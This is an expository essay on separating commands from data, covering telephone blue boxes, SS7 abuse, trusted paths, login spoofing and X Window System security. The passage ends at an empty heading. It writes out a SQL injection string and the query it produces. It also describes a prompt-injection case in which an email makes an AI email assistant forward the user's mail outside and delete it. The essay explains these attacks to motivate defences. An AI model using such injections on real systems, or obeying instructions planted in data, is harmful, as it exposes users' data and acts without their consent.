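# Separating trusted commands from untrusted data: trusted paths, capability systems, Qubes OS and language-model agents

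## Commands, data and the channel they share

A two-channel architecture carries the commands a system obeys on a path that untrusted programs and data cannot write to or imitate. Everything else, such as the documents a person opens or the messages strangers send, travels on another path, and the system never treats it as a command. Engineers have built this separation into login screens, window systems and whole operating systems, and more recently into assistants that run on language models. These designs differ considerably in what they separate and in the drawbacks of separating it, but they all address the same fault. A machine that receives commands and content through one channel can tell them apart only by their form. The American telephone network had this fault for decades, and its history shows both how engineers repaired it and what problems the repair left unsolved.

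### Tones on the voice path

In the 1950s, long-distance calls passed over trunks, the lines between switching offices. Each office had to signal to the next whether a trunk was free and which number the caller wanted. Short lines used direct current for this. Many long trunks had no conductor for it, so Bell engineers sent an audible tone down the same circuit that carried the conversation, which is called in-band signalling. *In-Band Single-Frequency Signaling* (Weaver and Newell, 1954) described the version that used a 2,600 Hz tone. The tone was on when the trunk was idle and off when it was in use, and relays at the far end responded to it. The method worked on any line good enough for speech and needed no extra wire, which made it attractive for a national network.

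The designers knew that a voice could produce the tone by accident. They picked a high frequency because false signals became rarer as the frequency rose. They also gave the receiver a guard circuit, which used energy elsewhere in the voice band to oppose the signal, since speech usually spreads over many frequencies. In one series of observations on trunks out of New York, Weaver and Newell counted 69 false signals, of which speech caused 48 and an adult whistling caused two. These precautions protect against accidental tones, but someone producing the tone deliberately will put little energy into other frequencies, which leaves the guard circuit almost none to use against the signal.

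The code made the fraud possible. A caller dialled a free number, and the local office recorded a free call. Once the trunk was connected, the caller played a 2,600 Hz tone into the mouthpiece. The far office registered the trunk as idle and dropped its end of the call, but the local office kept the line open because the caller had not hung up. When the tone stopped, the far office registered a new call and waited for a number. The caller sent one in a second code. *Common Channel Interoffice Signaling* (Bell System Technical Journal, 1978) explains that this code used pairs of tones, drawn from a set of six, for digits and control signals. The call went through, and the billing record still showed the free number. A toy whistle from a cereal box could make the first tone, and a pocket device known as a blue box could make all the tones.

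It was late for AT&T to try to keep the tones secret, because they were already in print. *Some Historical Documents*, on the website History of Phone Phreaking, lists a 1949 paper as the first public description of the multifrequency code that its author knows of, and Weaver and Newell published the 2,600 Hz figure in 1954. Slate's *Secrets of the Little Blue Box* (2011), a reprint of an *Esquire* article of October 1971, quotes a maker who claimed an order for a thousand boxes at $300 apiece. Changing the tones would have been expensive, because single-frequency signalling needed equipment at both ends of every voice channel, and any new tone would still have passed through a circuit on which callers could listen, record and play back. The security technologist Bruce Schneier concludes in *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity* that AT&T could deal with particular tricks, but the class of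 attack remained for as long as voices and commands shared a path.

### A separate network, and who can reach it

Separate signalling lines were an old idea by then. Bell tried one in 1922, using a telegraph circuit that carried the signals for 30 trunks at a time, and the installation between New York and Philadelphia ran through the 1940s. The method did not spread widely, because few routes had enough trunks to pay for it and the mechanical parts were costly to maintain. Computer-controlled switches changed the economics. In May 1976 Bell linked offices in Madison, Wisconsin, and Chicago through Common Channel Interoffice Signaling (CCIS), which sent digital messages over data links between the offices' processors. Each message identified the trunk it concerned. The voice circuit no longer carried commands, so the switches did not treat a whistle on it as one.

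Fraud was probably not the main motive. The Bell System Technical Journal lists slow speed first among the faults of the old tones, since a call over several links took 10 to 20 seconds to connect, and mentions fraud only briefly, under interference. The protection against fraud also came gradually. AT&T's *Common Channel Interoffice Signaling Intertoll Signaling Links* (1978), an internal manual, claims only a reduction in blue-box fraud and says that eliminating it completely depends on converting the whole network. A caller could still play the tone on a call that crossed even one old trunk. Signaling System 7 (SS7), which is based on the same separation, became a standard for telephone networks in the 1980s.

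Schneier places the new command path between the telephone and the switch, while the Bell documents place it between switches. Subscribers therefore still dial over the ordinary line, and some commands still travel in-band. But the local office accepts from that line only requests that any subscriber may make, so a caller can no longer pose as another telephone exchange.

All this assumed that only telephone companies could reach the signalling network. *Bad Connection*, an April 2026 report by the Canadian research group Citizen Lab, describes why that assumption no longer holds. SS7's designers wrote it for a closed community of operators, and it gives a receiving network no way to verify who sent a message or whether someone altered it. Over a thousand operators now interconnect. Some lease out their global titles, the addresses used to route signalling messages between networks, and intermediaries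 sell indirect access. A surveillance firm that gets in by any of these routes can send commands that look like a legitimate operator's.

Citizen Lab traced two such campaigns. In November 2024 one group tried to locate a company executive through several 3G and 4G networks. Another group sent a text message with hidden commands meant to make the phone's SIM card report the phone's location. This repeats the earlier fault of carrying commands inside messages, this time at the phone. The FCC's *Public Safety and Homeland Security Bureau Requests Comment on Implementation of Measures* (2024), a notice from the US communications regulator, quotes an advisory council's finding that such location queries yield a cell or a general area, not GPS coordinates. Interception is more serious. Ofcom's *Global Titles and Mobile Network Security*, a statement by the British regulator, cites evidence that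 attackers have used British global titles to capture the text messages that carry login codes.

Ofcom responded in April 2025 by banning new leases of global titles, and it set April 22, 2026 as the date on which the ban would reach existing leases, with some exceptions. The ban restricts one means of access but does not stop intruders who take over a legitimate operator's equipment. *SilentAir Hackers Intercept Calls, SMS From Inside Mobile Networks* (Kovacs, 2026) reported that the security company Enea found a group had hijacked nodes inside mobile networks to intercept calls and messages, mostly those of Taiwanese subscribers. Separation keeps callers out of the command channel but does not authenticate whoever is already in it. Authentication would address the leasing problem more directly than a ban, and Diameter, the standard for 4G signalling, supports it, but according to Citizen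 Lab, operators have largely failed to put it into use.

### The same fault in a database query

Websites commonly send commands to a database in SQL, a query language written as text. Suppose that a shop looks up orders by a name that the customer types into a form. The careless way is to paste the name into the middle of the command:

```
"SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
```

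If the customer types `Ana`, the database receives a request for the orders of the customer 'Ana'. If someone types `x' OR '1'='1` instead, the database receives this:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 'x' OR '1'='1'
```

The quotation mark after the x ends the name early, and the rest of the input becomes part of the command. Since '1'='1' is true for every row, the database returns everybody's orders. This attack is called SQL injection. Like the 2,600 Hz tone, the quotation mark is a signal meant for the system's own use, but anyone who can supply data can also supply it.

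A programmer can strip out quotation marks or mark them as harmless, but a filter of this kind has to anticipate every character and encoding that the database treats specially. The more reliable repair is a parameterised query. The program sends the command with a placeholder and hands over the name separately:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = ?
```

The database works out the structure of the command before it puts any value in place of the question mark. The same hostile input now starts a search for a customer whose name is literally `x' OR '1'='1`, and the search finds nobody. The placeholder can stand only for a value. If a programmer lets users choose something else, such as the name of the table, and pastes their choice into the command as text, that makes injection possible again. As with SS7, the repair does not establish who is asking, so a stranger who types `Ana` still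 gets Ana's orders unless the shop also checks logins.

### Some terms

A *channel* is any route by which one party's output can reach another party or affect its behaviour. Two channels can share the same wire. The SQL command and its value, for example, usually cross the same network connection, and the protocol's rules keep them separate.

Security engineers call a component *trusted* if its failure would break the security policy, and a source *trusted* if the system acts on its commands. Neither use implies that the component or source deserves trust. For example, every operator on the SS7 network is trusted, including one that rents its addresses to a surveillance firm.

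The *trusted computing base* is all the hardware and software that must work correctly for the policy to hold. If the shop's policy is that customers see only their own orders, the base includes the database, the login code, the operating system they run on and the processor. The code that resizes product pictures is outside the base, as long as something in the base stops it from reading the orders table. Designers try to keep the base small because people have to check it, and a fault anywhere in it can break the separation.

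A *capability* is an unforgeable reference that both names an object and grants the right to use it. An open file on a Unix system is close to a capability. When a user's command shell opens a letter and passes the open file to a spelling checker, the checker can read the letter through that reference and needs no permission to open any other file. A file name is not a capability, because any program can write down any name, and the system must decide by other means whether to allow the request. SS7 source addresses have the same weakness. Some operating systems grant all access through capabilities.

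A *covert channel* is a way to pass information through something that wasn't meant for communication. For example, suppose two programs share a processor but aren't allowed to exchange messages. The first program keeps the processor busy for a second to send a one and leaves it alone for a second to send a zero. The other program reads the bits by timing its own work. Covert channels can leak secrets even when a system's official channels are secure, and they are hard to remove while programs share hardware.

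### Two guarantees

When a person is using a screen, it matters where the picture came from as well as where the command came from. A system can establish one without establishing the other.

The first guarantee is that a command the system treats as the user's really came from the user. It fails if a malicious program can use artificial clicks to press the "Allow" button in a permission dialog. The second guarantee is that a message displayed as the system's own really came from the system. It fails if a malicious program can draw a convincing copy of the password prompt and collect what the user types.

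A trusted path is a connection between a person and the trusted part of the system that no other program can intercept, alter or imitate. It is meant to guarantee both that commands come from the user and that the messages the user sees come from the system, and formal criteria for secure systems came to require one. Suppose a computer has only the first guarantee because it accepts approvals only from the physical mouse, so no program can fake a click. If a program can still cover the real dialog with a picture about a routine update, and let the click pass through to the button underneath, the user gives a genuine command while believing it to be a different one. Now suppose a computer has only the second guarantee because it reserves a strip of the screen for the system's own messages, which no other program can draw on. If programs can inject keystrokes, a user who watches the strip may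 read an accurate report of an action that nobody requested.

### Agents and prompt injection

Language models have brought the shared channel back. An agent is a language model connected to tools that let it act on the world; an email assistant, for example, may have tools to search, send and delete mail. The model works from a context window, a single sequence of tokens (short pieces of text) that holds the developer's instructions, the user's request and whatever the tools have fetched. Suppose the user asks for help with the morning's mail. The software copies the new messages into the window, and one from a stranger contains an instruction to forward the three most interesting recent emails to an outside address, then delete them and the message itself. In Schneier's version of this example, the assistant complies. This is prompt injection, an attack in which a language model follows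 text supplied as data as if it were an instruction. The stranger needed only an address to write to, not a password or access to the user's machine. The first guarantee has failed because the system acted on a command that did not come from the user, and the deletions remove the most obvious evidence from the screen. Schneier likens the available defences to AT&T's work on its tones, because developers can block a particular wording once they have seen it, but attackers can always write another. The repair for SQL does not carry over directly either, because it relies on a grammar that fixes where a value can go, and ordinary language has no such grammar. Whether a model can have two channels therefore depends on what it can learn in training.

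## Login screens and the secure attention key

A password identifies the user to the computer, but an ordinary login screen gives the user no proof of which program is requesting it. Login spoofing exploits this. Suppose a student logs in at a shared terminal and starts a program that clears the screen, prints the usual prompt and waits. The next person types a name and password. The program saves both, prints "Login incorrect" and ends the student's session, which brings up the real prompt. The victim assumes they mistyped, tries again and gets in. The student's program needs no special privileges, because any program may write to the screen and read what the user types into it. Today a web page can attempt the same attack by filling the screen with a picture of the login prompt.

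### Why a mark on the screen does not help

A logo, coloured border or other mark on the genuine login prompt doesn't help users tell it from a fake, because a program that imitates the prompt can copy the mark too.

A fake login screen can copy even a secret picture that the user chose in advance and insists on seeing before typing a password. The computer needs a username to select the picture, and it shows the picture to anyone who types that name. The student can enter the victim's name at the real prompt, note the picture and add it to the fake. On the web, an impostor site can do this while the victim waits, by passing the name to the real site and copying the picture it returns.

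A reserved part of the screen works if the system prevents every other program from drawing there. Trusted window systems used such areas for their security labels. This approach fails if any program can take over the whole display, and even a well-protected area depends on the user noticing when the label is missing.

With a secure attention key, the user presses a key or key combination that only the system can detect, instead of checking something that the system displays.

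### The requirement in the Orange Book

The US government made this idea a formal requirement in its Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria, usually called the Orange Book. The Department of Defense (1985) replaced the August 1983 edition with a revised one in December 1985. Its own departments had to use the book to evaluate systems for classified data, and manufacturers could use it as a guide to what the government would buy. The Orange Book sorts systems into four divisions, from D (lowest) to A (highest), and splits division B into classes B1, B2 and B3.

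The text of division B in *Orange Book Parts I and II* has no general trusted-path clause for B1. It does ask for a mechanism by which an authorised user and the trusted computing base can "reliably communicate" in one situation, when the user sets the security level of data passing through certain devices. The general requirement arrives at B2, and B3 extends it:

| | Class B2 | Class B3 |
|---|---|---|
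| Purpose | Initial login and authentication | Any occasion that needs a definite connection between user and trusted computing base, such as login or a change of security level |
| Who may start it | Only the user | The user or the trusted computing base |
| Isolation | Not specified in the clause | "logically isolated and unmistakably distinguishable from other paths" |

The wider purpose matters because a false message can also do damage after login. For example, an analyst working at an unclassified level may ask to move up to secret. If an ordinary program can fake the confirmation, the analyst may type secret material into an unclassified file.

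The change in who may start communication is harder to judge. Under the B2 rule, a user can simply never type a password without having just asked for the prompt. Any login prompt that appears uninvited is suspect, however good it looks. B3 also lets the system start communication, which is useful if it needs a decision in the middle of a session. But the user must then recognise a genuine message without having requested it. That is probably why B3 also requires the path to be unmistakable, although the clause leaves the manufacturer to decide how.

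B3 also requires a trusted computing base small enough for people to analyse and test.

### From keystroke to prompt

A secure attention key is a key or combination of keys that the operating system reserves for starting a trusted path. The details vary, but the sequence is roughly this:

1. The user presses the keys, whatever the screen shows at the time.
2. The keyboard sends its codes to the operating system's kernel, the privileged core that controls the hardware. The kernel sees them before any application does.
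3. The kernel, or a trusted program working closely with it, recognises the combination and acts on it. Applications have no means of blocking it.
4. The system takes the screen and keyboard away from whatever was using them. Some systems kill the programs concerned, while others leave them running in the background.
5. The genuine login program draws its prompt and receives what the user types next.

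A secure attention key defeats even a perfect imitation of the login screen. If the fake includes the usual instruction to press the keys, a user who obeys replaces the fake with the real prompt. The fake cannot keep the screen by reacting to the keys, because the system takes over the screen regardless.

The secure attention key protects a password only if the kernel and the login program are intact and the user presses the key. It can't stop malicious code that has taken over the kernel, because that code is already on the trusted side of the path, or a device in the keyboard cable that records keystrokes before they reach the computer. If a fake login screen leaves out the instruction to press the key and asks for the password straight away, the user is protected only by remembering to press it anyway.

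### Ctrl+Alt+Del in Windows

Windows NT, which Microsoft released in 1993 and which underlies current versions of Windows, uses Ctrl+Alt+Del as its secure attention key. A system program called Winlogon handles the key combination. According to Microsoft's *Initializing Winlogon*, the program registers the combination as it starts up, before any application can claim it. Microsoft's *Responsibilities of Winlogon* adds that Winlogon has special hooks into the part of Windows that handles user input.

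Winlogon then creates three desktops, which here means separate screens that share one monitor, keyboard and mouse. One holds the user's applications, another holds the screen saver, and the third is Winlogon's own, for logins and other secure dialogs. When the user presses Ctrl+Alt+Del, Winlogon switches to its own desktop. The applications keep running, so the user can press the keys without losing work, but they cannot draw on Winlogon's desktop because they are on a different one.

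Older versions of Windows let other companies replace GINA, the component that asked for the password, and Winlogon gave the replacement access to the secure desktop. A badly written or malicious replacement would therefore have received passwords even when the trusted path worked correctly.

Administrators can drop the requirement to press the keys before signing in. Microsoft added this option for people whose physical impairments make the combination difficult, according to *Interactive logon*, its reference page for the setting. Microsoft also warns there that if users don't press the keys, malware can show a copy of the sign-in dialog and capture the password. People who sign in with a smart card don't have to press the keys, whatever the setting.

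Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about which machines have the requirement on by default. The *Interactive logon* page lists it as on for client computers running Windows 10 and 11. An older page lists it as on only for machines in an organisation's domain and off for stand-alone workstations, and the registry documentation for Windows 2000 lists it as on for the server edition and off for the professional edition. Where the requirement is off, users do not get into the habit of pressing the keys, so a prompt that appears without that step does not look odd.

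### The Linux key

Linux at first took a more drastic approach, killing any program that might be posing as the login prompt. Morton (2001), in *Linux Secure Attention Key (SAK) handling*, calls the key an "undefeatable way" of doing this and adds that users have to be taught to press it. Only the administrator can choose or change the key combination. Morton suggests Ctrl+Alt+Pause because Ctrl+Alt+Del already reboots the machine and Ctrl+Alt+Backspace already has a function in the X server, the program that draws the graphical desktop.

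The key kills every program that has the console (the system's main screen and keyboard) open. It also kills any running graphical desktop, which restarts with a new login prompt if the machine is set up for graphical login. A user who presses the key in the middle of a session therefore loses any unsaved work.

Morton concedes that the key also kills programs it should leave alone. It killed the mouse service gpm and the task scheduler Vixie cron because both kept the console open for no good reason. In one prominent Linux distribution, three lines in the startup scripts left the console open in every background service the scripts launched. An administrator could delete the lines, but this risked breaking system management tools. The kernel killed programs that had the console open, which on real systems was a poor sign that a program was imitating a login prompt.

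He also says he has heard that this is not a "true SAK" of the sort that class C2 requires, but does not know why. The Orange Book first makes the trusted path a general requirement at B2, two classes above C2, so C2 was the wrong class to cite. The key did have a real defect, though, which Poettering, a lead developer of systemd, the software that starts and manages services on most Linux distributions, described in posts on Mastodon. A user who has access to the console can open it again immediately after the kill. An attacker could, for example, keep a second program waiting that does not have the console open, so that it survives the kill and can then open the console. Poettering adds that pressing the key while systemd's own main process is writing a status message can kill that process, and the whole system with it.

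His project built a replacement that works more like the Windows one. According to the release notes for version 257 (systemd, 2024), systemd's login service responds to Ctrl+Alt+Shift+Esc by sending a signal that requests a secure login dialog. The service monitors the keyboard continuously, whichever session is in front. On receiving the signal, the display manager, the program that shows the graphical login screen, should switch to that screen and leave the old session running in the background.

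This arrangement puts more software inside the trusted computing base, because the path depends on several cooperating programs as well as the kernel. When a reader asked whether D-Bus, the message system that carries the signal, was robust enough, Poettering reasonably replied that if D-Bus fails, systemd will have serious problems anyway. If the display manager ignores the signal, the user keeps seeing whatever was already on the screen. GNOME's display manager has supported the signal since version 47, according to the Wikipedia article *Secure attention key*.

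### The secure desktop

Windows can also ask for a password after login, when a program needs administrator rights, through a feature called User Account Control. Microsoft's *How User Account Control works* explains that even an administrator normally runs programs with the rights of a standard user. When a program needs more, Windows dims the screen and shows a prompt on the secure desktop, which only Windows processes can access. Administrators see a consent prompt with Yes and No, while standard users see a credential prompt and have to enter an administrator's password.

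The secure desktop protects the user's mouse clicks as well as what the screen shows. Microsoft's *User Account Control* describes an attack on prompts that appear among ordinary windows, in which a program hides the real mouse pointer and draws a false one some distance away. When the false pointer is over something harmless, the real one is over the Allow button, so a click approves the request. On the secure desktop, the program can't draw a false pointer or reach the dialog.

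But the system opens this prompt without the user pressing a special key. B3 allows that only if the prompt is unmistakable, and this one is not, since Microsoft acknowledges that malware can imitate the whole secure desktop. If the user clicks Yes on a fake consent prompt, the malware gains nothing, because the click never reaches Windows. A fake credential prompt, however, may collect a real password. Microsoft points out that the password does not by itself raise the malware's rights, that other protections limit its use, and that the malware must already be on the machine.

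Faking a consent prompt is therefore harmless, because clicking Yes has an effect only if Windows receives the click, whereas a fake credential prompt can capture a password that an attacker can use later. Microsoft recommends a standard account as the more secure way to run Windows, but standard accounts show the credential prompt by default. The recommendation is probably still right, since a standard account limits what malware can do, but it trains people to type an administrator's password when the screen dims.

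Windows has a policy meant to close this gap by requiring a trusted path for entering credentials, but Microsoft does not recommend it. *Asking for clear written documentation that "Require trusted path for credential entry" is no longer recommended* (2019), a post on Microsoft's developer blog, describes a customer who wanted written confirmation that the advice had changed, although Microsoft had never recommended the policy. It had appeared in a draft of a government security baseline and was quickly removed, and a Microsoft specialist had given a talk demonstrating how useless it was. One weakness is that malware can show a fake prompt that leaves out the step of pressing the secure attention key, so the policy helps only users who notice the omission.

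### Whether people notice

Web browsers are especially vulnerable to login spoofing because they let strangers draw on the user's screen. Ye and Smith (2002), in *Trusted Paths for Browsers*, showed that a malicious site could imitate the signs of a secure connection, including the browser's certificate window. To prevent such forgeries, they designed a browser that switched the style of its window borders at random moments, while a separate reference window changed in step. A site could draw a changing border, but the timing was unpredictable, so a forged window would fall out of step with the reference window.

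Ye and Smith built a prototype in the Mozilla browser, and their user studies supported the design. It protects well against copying because the mark changes too unpredictably for a page to reproduce. But users have to compare two borders while trying to do something else, and even those who can tell a real border from a false one may forget to look.

In *The Emperor's New Security Indicators*, Schechter, Dhamija and colleagues (2007) tested whether people pay attention to such indicators. They asked 67 bank customers to do ordinary online banking tasks, with stronger signs of danger at each login. First they removed the browser's indicators of an encrypted connection. Next they removed the site-authentication image, a picture that the customer had chosen and was supposed to check before typing a password, and put up a notice saying that the feature was being upgraded. Finally they replaced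 the password page with a warning. Some participants used their own accounts, while others played a role with an invented one.

Nobody withheld a password when the encryption indicators disappeared. When the image disappeared, 23 of the 25 participants using their own accounts still typed their passwords. Role players behaved less securely than these participants, so studies that rely on role play may exaggerate carelessness, and the figure of 23 in 25 deserves the most weight. Even that figure comes from a small group in a laboratory, where people may assume that the researchers will protect them. The upgrade notice that explained the missing image is realistic, though, because an attacker who cannot reproduce a mark can always give an excuse for its absence.

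*Operating System Framed in Case of Mistaken Identity* (Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues, 2012) reports a later experiment with similar results. People recruited online tried out web games, and one of the sites displayed a fake operating-system window that asked for their computer password. In the most successful version of the attack, as many as 20% typed a password they later admitted was genuine. Of these experiments, this one most closely resembles login spoofing, and the participants were using their own computers.

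*The Web's Identity Crisis* (Thompson, Shelton and colleagues, 2019) reports a much larger test in Google's Chrome browser. Chrome used to show the verified legal name of some websites' owners beside the address. When the researchers removed the name for some users, most measures of behaviour did not change. Unlike the laboratory studies, this test observed people during their ordinary browsing, but it measured their reactions to a missing name on genuine sites, not to fraud.

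All of these experiments concern signs that people have to notice, and none measures how often people press an attention key when a prompt looks suspicious. Unlike a passive sign, compulsory Ctrl+Alt+Del doesn't rely on the user being suspicious, because pressing the keys is part of logging in. But it protects only the prompts that the user reaches that way, so someone who presses the keys at every login may still type the same password into a false window later.

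### What the user agrees to

A trusted path establishes which program receives the user's input, but the user may still misunderstand what they are approving. Suppose someone downloads a video player that contains malware, and the installer requests administrator rights. Windows displays a genuine prompt on the secure desktop, coloured grey if a verified publisher signed the program and yellow if it is unsigned or not trusted. The user clicks Yes. The malware gets administrator rights, even though the prompt and the click are both authentic and no other program has interfered with the screen or mouse.

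The prompt shows which program is making the request, but not what the program will do once approved. The approval also covers more than it appears to, because programs that the installer starts inherit its rights without a new prompt. Users who tire of the prompts can set the control to "Never notify", and Windows then approves every request from an administrator without a prompt. Approval prompts for agents have the same problem, and agents' requests can be much harder to summarise in a dialog box.

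## The X Window System and its trusted versions

After login, a user does almost everything through a display server, the program that controls the screen, keyboard and mouse and shares them among applications. It receives every password typed into a window, displays every prompt, and carries text between programs when the user copies and pastes. If it lets programs interfere with one another, it can undo separation that the operating system enforces elsewhere. Two programs that may not open each other's files could then obtain the same information from screen images, keystrokes or clipboard text.

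For decades most Unix and Linux desktops ran X11, the version of the X Window System that MIT released in 1987. *Design of the EROS Trusted Window System* (Shapiro, Vanderburgh and colleagues, 2004) traces X11's assumptions to the Xerox Alto, an early personal computer whose designers expected applications to be friendly and wanted them to cooperate. The paper quotes an X manual that gives the aim of version 11 as specifying "mechanism, not policy". The server supplies ways to draw and to exchange messages, and programs decide how to use them.

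### How X trusts its clients

In X, applications are clients that connect to the display server, on the same machine or over a network, and send it requests. According to *Securing The X Window System With SELinux* (Kilpatrick, Salamon and Vance, 2003), the server restricts who may connect but not what a client does afterwards. The basic protocol has 120 operations on at least 15 types of object, and clients refer to objects such as windows by number. A client can look up or guess the numbers of other programs' windows, so the number, like a file name, is not a capability.

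Any client can watch the keyboard and mouse while the user is working in another program. It can also take over the input entirely, or cover the screen with an invisible window that collects clicks. Some of these abilities have legitimate uses, such as letting a screen lock keep keystrokes away from the programs behind it.

Any client can also copy the contents of any window, which is how screenshot tools work. Refusing the request that copies pixels would not be enough to stop this, because X also lets a program create a window with no background, which starts out containing whatever was on the screen beneath it. Kilpatrick and colleagues conclude that a secure server would have to force a background onto such windows.

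X clients can send one another fake keystrokes, which can become part of a command if the target is a terminal. They can also draw in one another's windows, so a genuine banking program may display a message that the bank never sent. X therefore can't guarantee that input came from the user or that a window's contents came from its program, and a trusted path needs both guarantees.

When a user copies text to the clipboard in X, the program that holds the text keeps it, rather than storing it in the server, and announces that it owns the selection. When another program pastes, it asks the owner for the text, and the owner attaches the text to the asking program's window as a property, a named piece of data. Shapiro and colleagues point out that the server cannot determine whether any user action authorised the request. A clipboard manager that records everything the user copies makes the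 same requests as a program collecting passwords.

In his slides *Securing X*, Packard, a long-standing X developer, suggests delivering input only to the program that owns the window and disabling the extensions that generate artificial input. He notes that this breaks accessibility. Someone who cannot use a keyboard may depend on software that types for them, and that software needs the same ability to generate input that an attacker would use.

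### Labels for classified work

American intelligence agencies had a narrower problem. Their analysts handled material from several compartments, which are subdivisions of classified information by subject. Two people may both have top-secret clearance while only one has access to the compartment for a particular satellite. *Compartmented Model Workstation* (Cummings, Fullan and colleagues, 1987) explains that the Defense Intelligence Agency wanted to use commercial workstations for this work and asked for a project to find out how to do so securely. The project took place at MITRE, a non-profit research organisation. Epstein's annotated bibliography (1992) identifies a November 1987 MITRE report by J. P. L. Woodward as the original requirements for what became known as the compartmented mode workstation.

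The requirements apply the government's rules for classified data to the objects in the display server. Each top-level window carries a visible label showing its security level, and applications must not be able to forge it. The screen must also show which window will receive the user's keystrokes. This supports the trusted path, which the specifications also require, because a user who does not know where keystrokes are going cannot safely type a password.

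MITRE used two kinds of label: a sensitivity level, which determines how the system protects an object and who may read it, and an information label, which describes the object's contents and does not affect access decisions. If an analyst types a note containing only public facts in a secret window, the system protects the note as secret, but the information label can record that its contents are unclassified. Without the second label, everything written in that window would come to count as secret. MITRE also built a prototype to show that a workstation could meet the requirements while running unmodified off-the-shelf software.

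Cut and paste has to respect the windows' security labels. An analyst may copy a paragraph from an unclassified window into a secret report, because the report has stronger protection. Copying in the other direction would release secret information, so the system has to refuse or require someone with authority to approve the transfer. That person can still make a mistake, because a picture can hide a second picture in colour differences too small to see.

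Oracle's *Solaris Trusted Extensions Developer's Guide* describes a commercial version of X whose security attributes include a sensitivity label and a trusted-path flag. This version always keeps the trusted-path window on top. A selection manager checks transfers between windows against the policy, and a configuration file supplied by Oracle lists the transfers that the system confirms automatically. Each entry in the file saves the user an interruption but lets one more kind of transfer through without anybody confirming it.

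### Splitting the server in Trusted X

One way to meet the requirements is to add label checks to the X server, which makes the whole server part of the trusted computing base. Class B3 of the Orange Book requires that base to be small, but Kilpatrick and colleagues describe the server as a large body of code that is hard to evaluate. The defence contractor TRW still aimed for B3, with funding from DARPA, the Pentagon's research agency. Its prototype, Trusted X (TX), ran on Trusted Mach, an operating system designed for high security.

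*Evolution of a trusted B3 window system prototype* (Epstein, McHugh and colleagues, 1992) describes how TRW moved from a large, complex trusted base to a simpler one through polyinstantiation, which means running a separate copy of a component for each security level. In the architecture that Epstein, McHugh and colleagues (1993) describe, the X server is ordinary, untrusted software. The system runs one copy of the server for each level in use and surrounds the copies with a small amount of trusted code.

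If an analyst has an unclassified mail program and a secret map open together, the system runs two X servers, one unclassified and one secret. Each program can connect only to the server at its own level. Each server handles fonts, drawing and windows for its own clients, as an ordinary X server would. The trusted code does the jobs that involve both levels, such as sharing the real screen and keyboard between the two servers and controlling what passes between them.

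If the mail program exploits a bug to take control of its X server, it gains access to the unclassified windows and whatever the analyst types into them, but not to the secret map, which belongs to a different server. In a design with one server that checks labels, the same bug would expose both levels, because the buggy server also enforces the policy. TRW's design keeps the levels separate even if most of X is unreliable, provided that the kernel and the trusted code around the servers are sound.

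The team aimed to keep the trusted window system to about 30,000 lines of code, but it is less clear whether they did. Shapiro and colleagues started with the same target, ended with under 4,500 lines, and call their system ten times smaller than Trusted X. This would put the Trusted X prototype nearer 45,000 lines, though the comparison is rough.

Running several copies also uses memory and processing time. That is tolerable for an analyst who works at two or three levels, but Kilpatrick and colleagues thought it might be impractical on a system with many security domains. Qubes OS later used even more of both by giving each virtual machine its own X server.

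Looking back in 2006, Epstein, the lead author of TRW's papers, described a working prototype that showed several classifications on one screen and let users paste from low windows to high ones. He recalled that people in the early 1990s expected multilevel versions of Unix workstations to spread as the ordinary machines became cheap and common. The multilevel versions did not spread. They tended to be slow and awkward, and their features lagged years behind those of ordinary products. The government frequently waived its requirement to buy them and eventually dropped it. Trusted X was designed for a market that barely appeared, so the fact that few people used anything like it is weak evidence against splitting the server.

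### What compatibility ruled out

Work on trusted versions of X uncovered design flaws that, according to Shapiro and colleagues, engineers often could not fix without breaking compatibility with existing programs. Many of those programs depend on the flawed behaviour.

Cut and paste is hard to secure in X because one program has to write a property on another program's window to deliver copied text. A rule forbidding such writes would also stop pasting. The server can't simply allow properties that hold pasted text and block the rest, because programs use properties for many other purposes, including drag and drop and instructions to the window manager, and the program requesting the text chooses the name of the property that will carry it.

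Even a permitted paste, from an unclassified program to a secret one, sends some information from secret to unclassified. The secret program must request the text from the unclassified one, and it sets details of the request, such as the property name. A hostile program could encode secret data in those details. Designers therefore put a trusted selection manager between the two programs so that they don't communicate directly.

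That intermediary works only if applications use the clipboard as its designers expected. In *trusted X and cut&paste*, a message to an X developers' mailing list, Toth (2007) reported that while testing a multilevel version of Linux, he found that GNOME's terminal program used the selection protocol in ways that earlier selection managers could not support. After talking to others, he suspected that this was only a small part of the problem, and he did not think patching every application and window manager was viable. Solaris made properties easier to control by keeping separate copies for different levels by default, but Oracle also had to provide a file for exceptions.

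In X, the window manager is an ordinary client that moves, resizes and hides other programs' windows, so the desktop is unusable unless the window manager is trusted. A security extension added to X in 1996 divides clients into trusted and untrusted, and therefore always treats the window manager as trusted. The extension protects trusted clients from untrusted ones, but it does not protect untrusted clients from each other. Packard observes that most clients run as trusted, so the extension has little effect.

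Some leaks use only permitted requests. If one program moves a window off another, the server may send the second program a notice to redraw the newly visible part. The first program can cover and uncover the window in a pattern, and the second can read the pattern as a message. Blocking this covert channel would mean withholding redraw notices that many programs need to display their windows properly.

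### Hostile programs in one compartment

Labels control what moves between compartments. Shapiro and colleagues complain that the compartmented mode effort gave almost no attention to hostile programs inside a compartment, and they make the same criticism of the Orange Book. Their example is a malicious script that imitates another program's request for a password. If both run at the unclassified level, the policy allows information to move between them.

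In Trusted X, all the unclassified programs share one ordinary X server, so they can watch one another's keystrokes and copy one another's windows as they could on a machine with no security features. This was arguably a reasonable choice for the Defense Intelligence Agency, whose main worry was the release of secrets to people without clearance. Most other users have no classification levels, so their email, banking and downloaded games all run in effectively a single compartment. A system that protects only the boundaries between compartments does not protect these programs from one another.

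One approach is to create many more compartments. Kilpatrick and colleagues planned to bring X under SELinux, a set of controls from the US National Security Agency that lets administrators place programs in separate domains with specific permissions. Their design labels windows, fonts, cursors and other shared objects, and the server checks a permission before it carries out a request. A trusted window manager relabels the stream of keystrokes to match the window in use, so the policy can prevent other programs from reading it. Ordinary programs would still run unmodified. If the policy blocked a paste, for example, the program would find the clipboard empty.

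This could protect one unclassified program from another, but the user would see less. Kilpatrick and colleagues doubted that a window system could label so many domains distinctly enough for people to tell them apart. They also left covert channels and server bugs out of scope. The design addressed hostile requests from clients, but the large X server remained in the trusted computing base.

### Wayland

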